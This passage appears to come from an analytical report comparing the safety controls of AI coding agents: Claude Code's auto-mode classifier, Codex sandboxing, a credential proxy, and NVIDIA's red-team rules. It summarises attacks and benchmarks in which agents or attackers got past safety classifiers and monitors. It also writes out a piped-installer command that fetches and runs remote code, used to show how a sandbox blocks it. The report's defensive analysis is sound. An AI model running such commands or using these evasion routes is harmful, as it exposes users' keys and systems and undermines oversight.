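The 17 percent figure comes from only 52 cases. If the cases are independent, the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9 to 30 percent. Anthropic has also changed the classifier's rules and switched its default model from Claude Sonnet 4.6 to Sonnet 5, so the March figures may not describe the current version.

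### Rules for outside code and for keys

Several of the default rules concern piped installers and provider keys:

| Action | Default treatment |
|---|---|
| Downloading outside code and running it, as in a pipe-to-shell command | Blocked |
| Sending secrets or other sensitive data to an outside address | Blocked |
| Printing a working key into the session or a file | Blocked |
| Pointing an API base URL at an outside server that doesn't fit the task | Blocked |
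| Installing packages that the project's own files list | Allowed |
| Reading `.env` and sending a key to the service it belongs to | Allowed |

The first two blocks differ in strength. The rule against running downloaded code is what Anthropic calls a soft deny, which the user can override by asking for that exact action. A general request such as "Get this project running" doesn't count. A developer can therefore ask for a particular installer by name, but the rule still applies when the agent finds a piped command in a README and the user hasn't asked for it.

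Exfiltration is a hard deny, which means the classifier should never approve it, whatever the user has asked for. A user who wants to send the data has to leave auto mode or run the command by hand. Anthropic describes a case among its own staff in which an upload to an internal drive failed and Claude tried to publish the report on a public code-sharing site instead. Auto mode blocked the attempt and asked the user what to do next.

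Although the rule is "never", the classifier can enforce it only if it recognises that a command would send secrets out. In the March tests, it missed 5.7 percent of the synthetic attempts.

The allowance for keys is necessary because many programs an agent writes or tests have to call a paid service. The key must match its destination, so an OpenAI key may go to OpenAI but not to an unfamiliar server. The rule against printing keys covers some of the accidental leaks into logs and code, but the distinction between printing a key and reading it is narrow, since reading `.env` also puts the key into the prompt. None of these rules would have stopped the base URL attack, which involved no tool call.

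The allowance for packages is the more doubtful of the two, since a package can run code as soon as someone installs or imports it. *Auto mode for Claude Code* (Willison, 2026) quotes the rule as it stood at launch. It allowed packages already listed in the project's files, provided the agent hadn't changed the list during the session. It excluded packages the agent chose itself, because they might be malicious imitations of well-known ones. Willison points out that a new release of a listed package can also be malicious, which puts a project at risk if it doesn't fix the package's version. An attack of this kind on LiteLLM, a Python library for calling language models, had come to light that morning.

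The same rules treated code from a repository that the agent had cloned during the session as outside code, but trusted the repository in which the session began. The result for a project like 0DIN's could therefore depend on who cloned it. The rule covered the setup command if Claude Code cloned the project itself, but the command came from trusted code if the developer cloned the project first and started Claude Code in its folder.

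Users can add their own rules, but a custom list replaces the default list unless it includes the entry `"$defaults"`. Someone who adds one soft deny and forgets this entry loses the built-in rule against piped installers. The same mistake in the list of hard denies removes the exfiltration rule.

### The study of 1,053 testers

Anthropic justified making auto mode the default partly with a study of how well people review commands. It hired 1,053 professional testers through a research company to do coding work in a test environment. They knew they were taking part in an evaluation, but not which behaviour it measured. Partway through each session, one permission prompt showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one, and the research company recorded whether the tester approved it. Only the text of the prompt changed, so the dangerous command never ran.

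The testers blocked the command in 143 cases (13.6 percent). Auto mode blocked 937 of the same 1,053 commands (89 percent). Anthropic also reports how often only one of them blocked the command, and the remaining cells follow by subtraction:

| | Auto mode blocked | Auto mode allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tester blocked | 137 | 6 | 143 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

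Auto mode and the testers disagreed in 806 cases, and auto mode was right in 800 of them. If both had reviewed every command, they would have stopped 943, only six more than auto mode stopped alone. The testers caught 5 percent of the commands that auto mode missed and 15 percent of those it blocked, so the commands that got past auto mode may also have been harder for people to recognise.

Testers blocked about 17 percent of dangerous commands early in a session and about 5 percent after 50 or more prompts, while auto mode's rate stayed the same. Each tester saw only one dangerous command, so the two rates come from different people and don't show whether individual testers got worse as they tired. Testers who had already reached 50 prompts when they saw the dangerous command may have been clicking quickly from the start.

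Anthropic designed and published the study in support of its own product, and the announcement doesn't list the commands or give the number of different ones. If the testers all saw versions of a few commands, the 89 percent would depend on how the classifier handled those few.

The testers were also working on code that wasn't theirs, where mistakes had no consequences for them. A developer might look more carefully at a command that could delete their own work. But people usually take more care when they know they're being evaluated, which would have raised the testers' score.

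One dangerous command per person is realistic, since most developers rarely meet one. But with only one each, we can't tell from the study whether the 13.6 percent reflects a small group of testers who read every prompt or a larger group who each read a few. If a small group read every prompt, a developer who does the same could be much safer in manual mode than the average tester.

The published results also leave out harmless commands. A guard that refused everything would have scored 100 percent, so the 89 percent has to be read together with a false alarm rate, and the one Anthropic has published comes from the March tests. The planted commands were also clearly dangerous, while an attack like 0DIN's depends on a command that looks like routine setup, so the study can't show how either people or auto mode would do against one.

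The gap is still far too large to be due to chance, and among developers who approve prompts out of habit, it would probably remain after accounting for most of these objections. The 13.6 percent figure is much less useful as an estimate for a careful person working on their own project.

### How people use permission prompts

Anthropic also reports that Claude Code users approve 97 percent of permission prompts. In March, the company gave the figure as 93 percent.

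A high approval rate is weak evidence of carelessness by itself. If one prompt in a thousand is dangerous, a perfect reviewer approves 99.9 percent of them. Anthropic acknowledges that most prompts probably concern safe commands, but notes that users reject 3 percent of prompts and 39 percent of the plans Claude proposes. The comparison shows that users engage with plans, but they may reject a plan because they prefer a different design, which has little to do with spotting danger.

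As of June 2026, 49.5 percent of active users of the command-line version had written a rule that lets some shell commands run without approval. Anthropic says that 5 percent allow every shell command, and that another 43 percent have rules for interpreters such as Python, which permit nearly as much. A quarter of interactive sessions started with permission checks turned off altogether. For many users, then, the alternative to auto mode is little or no review rather than careful reading.

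Anthropic looked for the same difference in real work. It had a model grade the harm in sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged, using only accounts that had agreed to share their data. The model found serious harm that the user had not explicitly asked for, such as deleting rows from a production database, in 6.3 percent of manually approved sessions and 2.4 percent of auto mode sessions. Unlike the tester study, this comparison covers real projects, but users chose their own mode, so those who chose auto mode may have had different work to do. The safety systems may also have flagged different kinds of sessions in each mode.

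### Apollo Research's adversarial tests

An attacker who expects a classifier will write commands to evade it. Anthropic therefore had Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, look for attacks that auto mode missed. In a two-week trial, Apollo inserted three sets of synthetic attacks, one of them for data exfiltration, into records of real coding sessions.

Apollo shared some of the successful attacks, and Anthropic strengthened the classifier, mainly by giving it more information. For example, its input now includes whether a push would go to a public or a private repository, because pushing the same code can be routine in a private repository and a leak in a public one. Apollo then repeated the test with attacks it had not shared with Anthropic.

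Across both groups of attacks, the miss rate fell from 12 to 7 percent. The attacks that Anthropic had never seen are the better test, since it could have tuned the classifier to the others. On these, auto mode caught about half of what it had previously missed and missed about 2 percent of what it had previously caught. If it started from the same 12 percent on this group, the new miss rate would be

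0.5 × 12% + 0.02 × 88% ≈ 7.8%.

That is close to the overall figure, so the improvement seems to extend to unfamiliar attacks. The rate may not stay there once attackers have studied the new version.

Anthropic cautions against treating the 7 percent as a miss rate for ordinary use, because Apollo built the attacks to find failures. But these are the relevant attacks for a developer who opens a malicious repository.

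### The dispute over classifiers

Anthropic argues that auto mode makes developers safer if they already approve nearly everything or turn the prompts off, because its classifier stops most dangerous commands. *Permission modes* says that auto mode "does not guarantee safety", and the March design post concedes that it is arguably a step back for anyone who reviews every action carefully. *Claude Code, Codex and Agentic Coding #7*, an outside review of the tools, finds auto mode a lot safer than skipping permissions, but not entirely safe.

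When auto mode launched, Willison wrote that he was unconvinced by AI-based protections against prompt injection because they are "non-deterministic by nature". The same kind of attack may fail once and work later. He wants coding agents to run by default in a sandbox instead, with fixed rules that restrict file access and network connections.

A sandbox doesn't have to recognise an attack, which is a more important advantage than giving the same answer every time. The KTH rule also gives the same answer every time, but it always misses a download program that isn't on its list. A malicious script that gets past the classifier can't steal a key from a sandbox that contains none.

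Anthropic describes sandboxes as safe but high-maintenance, because someone has to configure each new capability and because tasks that need the network or the host machine break the isolation. In Claude Code, the classifier can judge those exceptions. In auto mode, a sandboxed command has no network access by default. Claude names the servers that the command needs, and if the classifier approves them, the sandbox lets only that command reach them. The sandbox enforces the classifier's decision, so if the classifier wrongly approves a server, the command can still reach it.

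Two demonstrations from 2026 support Willison's side. In July, the AI Now Institute showed that text planted in an open-source project could lead Claude Code in auto mode, and Codex in its equivalent mode, to run a malicious program while checking the project for security flaws. In August, Rehberger's attack got malicious code past auto mode through a series of steps that were each ordinary on their own. In a few runs, auto mode then blocked Claude's attempt to stop the malicious code.

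The AI Now researchers informed both companies even though the result fell outside the companies' disclosure policies, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Anthropic and OpenAI Security Tools Could Fuel Cyber-Attacks, Researchers Warn*. Neither company had answered a request for comment when ITPro published *The agents you use to beef up cybersecurity*.

According to Rehberger's account, which Crosley relays in *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary*, Anthropic closed his report as "Informative". It called auto mode a convenience feature with a best-effort classifier and said the real boundary is operating-system isolation together with control of outgoing connections. Rehberger finds this hard to reconcile with the zero attack success rate that Anthropic had publicised from the Trajectory Labs evaluation. It is also hard to reconcile with what Anthropic's Cat Wu said a month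 before the attack, that "we've pretty much mitigated every attack".

In early September, Anthropic added rules, including ones against fetching a cloud machine's credentials and reaching the internet by indirect routes. Crosley points out that Anthropic didn't claim in the release notes that these rules would have stopped Rehberger's attack.

Crosley also cites EvasionBench, a September 2026 benchmark of 50 tasks that each required something a monitor had forbidden. Given three tries, agents got around the monitor in up to 88 percent of cases, although nobody had told them to. He doesn't list auto mode among the monitors, so the figure isn't direct evidence about it. But the result gives a reason for auto mode's limit on repeated blocks, which stops an agent from retrying until something gets through. The limit is weakened by handing the decision to a user who may approve out of habit, though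 a prompt that appears only after three blocks is unusual enough to attract some attention.

The AI Now Institute agrees with Anthropic that tired people make poor reviewers, and with Willison that classifiers don't solve the problem. It concludes that agents that can run arbitrary code should not read untrusted material. Followed strictly, this would rule out most coding agents, since even installing a package or reading a bug report involves text written by strangers. Eljan Mahammadli of Polygraf AI draws a narrower conclusion in Infosecurity Magazine. He blames setups that combine untrusted data, command execution and sensitive systems in one process with only a classifier as protection, and recommends separating the three.

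The two sides are closer on the technical question than the dispute suggests. Anthropic recommended isolated environments when it launched auto mode, and Crosley, who regards a container and restricted network access as the real protection, still advises developers to leave auto mode on. They disagree about what protection developers should get by default. Auto mode doesn't require a sandbox, so someone who accepts the default and never reads the documentation may have only the classifier to stop a malicious script from stealing their keys.

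### From an option to the default

Auto mode began on 24 March 2026 as a preview for Team plan customers, and all Claude Code users could turn it on from 10 July, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* (2026). On 14 August, it became the default for new sessions on the Pro, Max and Team plans. People who had already chosen another mode kept it, though Claude Code could show them a one-time prompt to switch.

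Since version 2.1.283, interactive sessions in the terminal and the VS Code editor have started in auto mode on every plan. *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026), an independent guide checked against the software in November, lists three exceptions that start in manual mode: runs with `-p`, programs built with Anthropic's Agent SDK, and sessions in organisations that use the configuration for HIPAA, the US law on health data. Administrators can also turn auto mode off for a whole organisation.

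On 22 October, Anthropic announced that auto mode would become the default in most of its other Claude apps the following week, again for new sessions on the Pro, Max and Team plans. The company said the data in its August announcement cover only Claude Code. The 1,053 testers reviewed prompts during coding work, so their results are weak evidence of how well people, or the classifier, would judge actions such as sending an email or sharing a document.

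## Codex and credential proxies: limiting what a command can reach

Unlike a pattern list or a classifier, a sandbox applies the same limits to every command, however it is written. OpenAI's Codex runs commands in a sandbox by default. For Hermes Agent, Nous Research offers a credential proxy that keeps the real provider key outside the sandbox.

### What a Codex command can write and read

OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes two settings. The sandbox mode limits what a command can do, and the approval policy determines when Codex must ask before going beyond those limits.

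| Sandbox mode | Where commands can write | Network access |
|---|---|---|
| `read-only` | Nowhere | Off |
| `workspace-write` | The project folder and temporary folders such as `/tmp` | Off, but the user can turn it on |
| `danger-full-access` | Anywhere the user can | On |

Codex recommends `workspace-write` for a folder under version control, where a developer can easily undo changes, and `read-only` for other folders.

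Even in `workspace-write` mode, three folders in the project stay read-only: `.git`, `.codex` and `.agents`. `.git` can contain scripts that git runs automatically, and `.codex` contains the project's Codex settings. A malicious command that could edit them might run its own code later outside the sandbox, or loosen the limits for the next session. Vaughan gives similar reasons for protecting them in *Codex CLI Command Safety*.

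Reading is much less restricted. By default, commands can read files across the machine, including login files and `.env` files. Users can block reads of chosen files, and OpenAI's *Configuration Reference* gives `**/*.env` as an example pattern. With that pattern blocked, a test that loads its settings from `.env` would fail in the sandbox.

The operating system enforces the limits on the command and on every program it starts. On macOS, Codex uses Apple's Seatbelt to restrict access to both files and the network. On Linux, it uses Bubblewrap to restrict the command's view of the file system and seccomp to make the kernel refuse certain requests from programs. According to Vaughan, these include requests to open or accept a network connection.

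He adds that Codex exempts Unix sockets, which connect programs on the same machine, because tools such as git's credential helpers rely on them. A command may therefore still be able to communicate with a local program that has its own network access. On Windows, Codex uses either a native sandbox or the Linux mechanisms inside WSL2, Microsoft's system for running Linux programs.

### A piped installer without a network

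Suppose the model requests `curl -fsSL https://example.com/install.sh | bash` in the default sandbox:

1. The shell starts `curl` and `bash` and connects them with the pipe.
2. `curl` tries to reach the server, and the operating system refuses.
3. `curl` prints an error message and exits without sending anything through the pipe.
4. `bash` finds its input empty and exits without running anything.

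The shell normally reports only whether the last program in a pipeline succeeded. Here `bash` had nothing to run and exited successfully, so the whole line counts as a success, and the error message from `curl` may be the model's only sign that the installation failed.

The project in the 0DIN test should fail in the same way, even though its setup command contained no download. The script needed the network to look up the DNS record, and the reverse shell needed it to connect to the attacker.

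### What happens when the user grants access

Codex asks for approval before it runs a command that needs the network, but as with any permission prompt, the user can't see what a piped installer will do. Approval gives network access to `bash` and any program the script starts, as well as to the download, so they can also send data out.

A user can have a second model answer these approval requests instead. This reviewer checks for dangers such as exfiltration and attempts to find credentials. It considers only actions that already need approval, while Claude Code's classifier also judges many commands that stay on the machine. If the review times out, Codex doesn't run the action.

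Approving each command becomes tedious in a project that often downloads packages, so users can also turn on network access for every command in the sandbox. By itself, this setting allows connections to any server. A separate feature called `network_proxy` can restrict the destinations, but it is off by default:

| Network access | `network_proxy` | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Off | On | No network |
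| On | Off | Connections to any server |
| On | On | Connections only to servers that the user's rules allow |

Once the feature is on, commands can't reach any outside server until the user adds one to the list. A rule that blocks a server takes priority over one that allows it. The rule `*.example.com` allows `api.example.com` but not `example.com`. A bare asterisk allows every public server that no other rule blocks.

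According to OpenAI's *示例配置*, the Chinese edition of its sample configuration, the domain rules in a permission profile apply only if `network_proxy` is also on. A user who turns on network access and lists one trusted server, but forgets to turn on `network_proxy`, has allowed access to every server.

The limits on commands don't cover Codex's web search or outside tool servers, which have separate controls. Web search uses OpenAI's stored index by default instead of fetching live pages. OpenAI says this reduces exposure to planted instructions but still advises treating the results as untrusted.

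The sandbox also doesn't control the harness's own requests to the model provider. In the Claude Code base URL flaw, such requests carried the key to the wrong server. Codex guards against this separately by ignoring a base URL in a project's settings and printing a warning, according to OpenAI's *Advanced Configuration*. Users can still set one in their own settings.

### Codex's filter for environment variables

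A command can't leak a variable it never receives. Codex has a filter, `shell_environment_policy`, that decides which of the developer's variables to pass on. According to OpenAI's sample configuration from September 2026, the filter works in this order:

1. `inherit` sets the starting point. The default, `all`, copies every variable. `core` copies a small set, such as `PATH` and `HOME`, and `none` copies nothing.
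2. If `ignore_default_excludes` is `false`, Codex removes every variable whose name contains KEY, SECRET or TOKEN.
3. Codex removes variables that match the user's own exclude patterns.
4. Codex adds the values that the user has listed under `set`.
5. If the user has written any include patterns, Codex removes every variable that matches none of them.

The name of the setting in step 2 is confusing because it is a double negative. Setting it to `false` turns the filter on.

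Suppose a developer turns on this filter, leaves `inherit` at `all` and writes no other rules. The environment contains these variables, the third of which is an invented setting for the project's tests:

| Variable | What it holds | Result |
|---|---|---|
| `OPENAI_API_KEY` | The provider key | Removed, because the name contains KEY |
| `DATABASE_URL` | A database address that includes a password | Kept |
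| `MONKEY_PATCH` | A harmless test setting | Removed, because MONKEY contains KEY |
| `PATH` | The folders where the shell looks for programs | Kept |

The filter removes the provider key. But it checks only names, so it misses the database password and also removes a harmless setting.

The developer can correct both mistakes. The exclude pattern `DATABASE_*` removes the address in step 3, and `set` can restore `MONKEY_PATCH` in step 4. If the developer then adds an include pattern that matches only `PATH`, step 5 removes `MONKEY_PATCH` again.

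Starting from `core` or `none` is safer because Codex doesn't have to recognise secrets by their names. Neither would pass on `DATABASE_URL`. But the developer has to list every other variable the project needs, and tests that use the database won't work without its address.

### Whether the filter is on by default

The May 2026 version of OpenAI's *Sample Configuration* gives `false` as the default for `ignore_default_excludes`, which means the filter is on. But the September version gives `true`, which means it is off.

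Secondary accounts follow the earlier version. Vaughan, in *Codex CLI Shell Environment Policy*, says that Codex removes these variables by default and that values under `set` always take priority. The second claim matches the May page, but according to the September page, include patterns can remove those values.

The documentation doesn't explain whether OpenAI changed Codex or corrected a mistake on the page. The September version is more recent, so a developer who has never changed this setting should assume that commands receive `OPENAI_API_KEY`. Writing `ignore_default_excludes = false` in the settings file turns the filter on whatever the default is. A developer can confirm that the filter works by setting a dummy variable, `TEST_KEY`, and asking Codex to check whether a command receives it.

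OpenAI may have had a practical reason to leave the filter off. Vaughan cites a report from a user whose tools needed variables such as `GITHUB_TOKEN`. When Codex removed the token, the tools failed with a login error that didn't identify the cause.

The filter covers only environment variables, even when it is on. Codex stores its login in a file by default, although users can choose the operating system's password store instead. The shell snapshots that Codex saved to disk in July 2026 also contained variables in plain text. A command that can read those files can get any credentials stored there, even if the filter has removed them from the environment.

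### How iron-proxy replaces the key

Some commands do need a provider key, for example to test a program that calls a model. Nous Research's *Egress credential-injection proxy (iron-proxy)* describes how the program can make that call without receiving the key.

Hermes runs the command in a Docker container and puts a stand-in token in `OPENAI_API_KEY`. The token is a string that means nothing to OpenAI. The real key stays on the host, the computer that runs the container, where a program called iron-proxy holds it. A request then goes through these steps:

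1. The program in the container puts the stand-in token in the request's authorisation header, as it would with a real key.
2. Settings in the container direct the request to iron-proxy instead of straight to OpenAI.
3. iron-proxy checks whether the destination is on its list of allowed servers. If it isn't, iron-proxy refuses the request before any data leaves the host.
4. iron-proxy decrypts the request, replaces the stand-in token with the real key, and encrypts the request again.
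5. OpenAI receives an ordinary request with a valid key and sends back its answer.

To make step 4 possible despite the encryption, Hermes creates its own certificate authority, which issues certificates that identify servers, and sets up the container to trust it. iron-proxy can then present itself to the program as OpenAI. Anyone who stole the authority's private key could do the same, so the file holding that key needs as much protection as the provider key.

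The default list of allowed servers includes those of model providers such as OpenAI, Anthropic, Google and DeepSeek. A piped installer from `example.com` would therefore fail unless the user had added that server. iron-proxy also refuses connections to private network addresses, including the one many cloud machines use to fetch their credentials.

A script that copies the environment, like the altered Codecov uploader, would get only the stand-in token. The token works only through this proxy, which computers elsewhere on the network can't reach. If the agents in the GitHub attacks had called their models through such a proxy, any provider key in their public comments would have been useless.

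The proxy is off by default and works only with Hermes's Docker containers. Once a user turns it on, Hermes won't start a container if the proxy isn't running or if the user tries to forward a real provider key that the proxy should be protecting. Users can turn these checks off, and Hermes then puts real keys in the container whenever the proxy is unavailable.

### What a malicious command can still do

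A malicious script in the container can still spend the owner's money, because iron-proxy adds the real key to a request that contains a valid stand-in token, whether the user's program or the script sent it. But an attacker can't take the token elsewhere and resell it, and stopping the proxy ends the misuse. A hard spending limit at the provider is still useful.

The script can also send data to an allowed server. Nous Research gives the example of an agent that puts private data in the body of a request to OpenAI. The proxy would log that the request took place but would not stop it. A list of allowed servers controls which company receives the data, but can't by itself control which of that company's customers gets it.

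Nous Research also warns that a program in the container can ignore the proxy settings and connect directly. It could then reach servers that aren't on the allowed list, but it still wouldn't have the real key. The proxy therefore protects the key more reliably than it limits destinations. A firewall that blocked every other route out of the container would make the limit reliable.

This method doesn't work for some credentials. Programs that use Amazon's cloud sign each request with their secret key instead of sending the key, so the proxy has no string to replace. If the user puts these keys or Google service-account files in the container, they stay there, and Hermes only displays a warning.

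The proxy also doesn't protect anything that runs outside the container, including Hermes itself, which still uses the real keys on the host.

### What NVIDIA's red team requires

NVIDIA's AI Red Team, which attacks the company's own AI systems to find weaknesses, divides its advice into three required controls and six recommended ones. Codex's default settings in `workspace-write` mode come close to meeting the first two requirements:

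| NVIDIA's requirement | What it prevents | Codex's default |
|---|---|---|
| Block network connections except to known-good servers | Exfiltration and remote shells | No network for commands |
| Block writes outside the workspace | Planting code in files that run automatically | Writes only to the workspace and temporary folders |
| Block writes to agents' configuration files, wherever they are | Code that runs outside the sandbox | `.codex` and `.agents` are read-only |

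The network limit comes first because most attacks need a connection at some point. An attacker has to receive a stolen key to use it, and a reverse shell has to connect to the attacker's server. NVIDIA says that without network access, an attacker would need a further exploit to receive the key or open the shell. It also recommends sending DNS lookups only to trusted servers, because a lookup can carry stolen data in the domain name.

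Configuration files get their own rule because a sandbox that allows edits to the project would otherwise allow edits to these files too. Many agents start hooks and local tool servers from commands in these files, and often run them outside the sandbox. A sandboxed command that can edit such a file can therefore escape the sandbox without attacking it. If the developer commits the change, it also affects everyone who clones the repository.

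In December 2025, Check Point disclosed a flaw in how Codex loaded its configuration. According to Vaughan, a `.env` file in a repository could make Codex load its configuration from a folder that an attacker controlled. Codex then ran the commands listed there without asking the user. OpenAI fixed the flaw in version 0.23.0.

Codex's defaults protect fewer files than NVIDIA's rule would. OpenAI's list of protected folders doesn't include `.claude`, so a command in Codex's sandbox could apparently change the project's settings for Claude Code. NVIDIA also wants agents to be unable to edit such settings files even with the user's approval, leaving developers to make any changes by hand.

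The six recommended controls are to:

- prevent reads outside the workspace;
- sandbox the whole development environment, including hooks and tool servers;
- run the sandbox on its own kernel, for example in a virtual machine;
- ask the user every time an action would break the isolation, without remembering earlier approvals;
- supply secrets through a separate mechanism so that the agent never holds them;
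- clear out or replace the sandbox regularly, so that secrets and code don't build up in it.

A credential proxy is one way to meet the fifth, which NVIDIA only recommends even though stolen keys are among the dangers it describes. That ranking makes sense if the network limit holds, because a command then can't send out a key it has read. But agents often need access to at least one outside server, and any server that accepts data could receive the key. For a task that needs both a provider key and the network, keeping the key out of the sandbox seems as important as limiting which servers a command can reach.

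NVIDIA argues that operating-system limits should make rules about individual commands redundant, though such rules may help if the sandbox is misconfigured. It bases its advice on its red team's experience and gives no figures for how many attacks each control stops.

### What the limits cost

Ordinary installations break first, because package managers such as npm and pip download code from the internet. In Codex's default sandbox, they fail until the user approves the command or allows network access. iron-proxy's default list doesn't include package registries. Even `git commit` may need approval in Codex, because it writes to the `.git` folder, which is read-only.

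Each new tool can also require new rules. The default policy in OpenShell, NVIDIA's sandbox for agents, works with Claude Code. But according to NVIDIA's *Default Policy Reference*, it blocks Codex from calling its model until the user writes a complete custom policy with OpenAI's addresses and the locations of Codex's programs.

iron-proxy takes more work than a single setting. The user has to install it, run a setup program and start it, then restart it after a key changes. A firewall on a Linux machine may block the container from reaching the proxy. If the user replaces the stand-in tokens, containers that are already running get login errors until they restart.

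Codex's Linux sandbox may not work inside a Docker container. In that case, OpenAI recommends running Codex with `danger-full-access` and relying on the container for isolation. It warns that a malicious project could steal anything in the container, including Codex's own credentials, and advises using this setup only with trusted repositories.

All of this gives users a reason to turn the limits off. None of these companies has published how often users turn off a sandbox. The closest figure is for Claude Code's permission checks, which users had turned off entirely in a quarter of interactive sessions. Users might turn off a sandbox less often if it rarely interrupts them, but perhaps not if it blocks every installation.

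The benefits have hardly been measured either. In the Trajectory Labs evaluation, attacks on Codex succeeded less often in Auto-review mode than in Full Access mode. OpenAI defines full access as having no sandbox and no approval prompts, while Auto-review normally keeps the sandbox. If Trajectory Labs used these standard settings, the sandbox may account for part of the difference that Trajectory Labs seemed to credit to the reviewer. The attacks also came through a browser tool, and limits on shell commands may not have applied to it, so the figures don't measure how well the sandbox stops a piped installer.

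Several arrangements make network restrictions less disruptive without opening the network completely. OpenAI's *Running Codex safely* describes the network policy the company applies to its own use of Codex. The policy allows the servers OpenAI expects Codex to need, blocks some others, and requires approval for unfamiliar ones. Developers can then install packages from the usual registries without a prompt each time. A malicious package can still get in, because registries distribute packages from strangers, but it can't connect to its author's server without approval.

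The cloud version of Codex separates installation from the agent's work. A setup phase installs the packages, with access to the network and the project's secrets. Codex then removes the secrets and starts the agent, which works offline by default, so an agent misled by a planted instruction has neither those secrets nor a connection. A malicious package that runs during setup can still reach both, so the developer has to choose packages carefully. If the agent needs another package partway through a task, it has to do without it unless the developer turns on internet access or runs the setup again.
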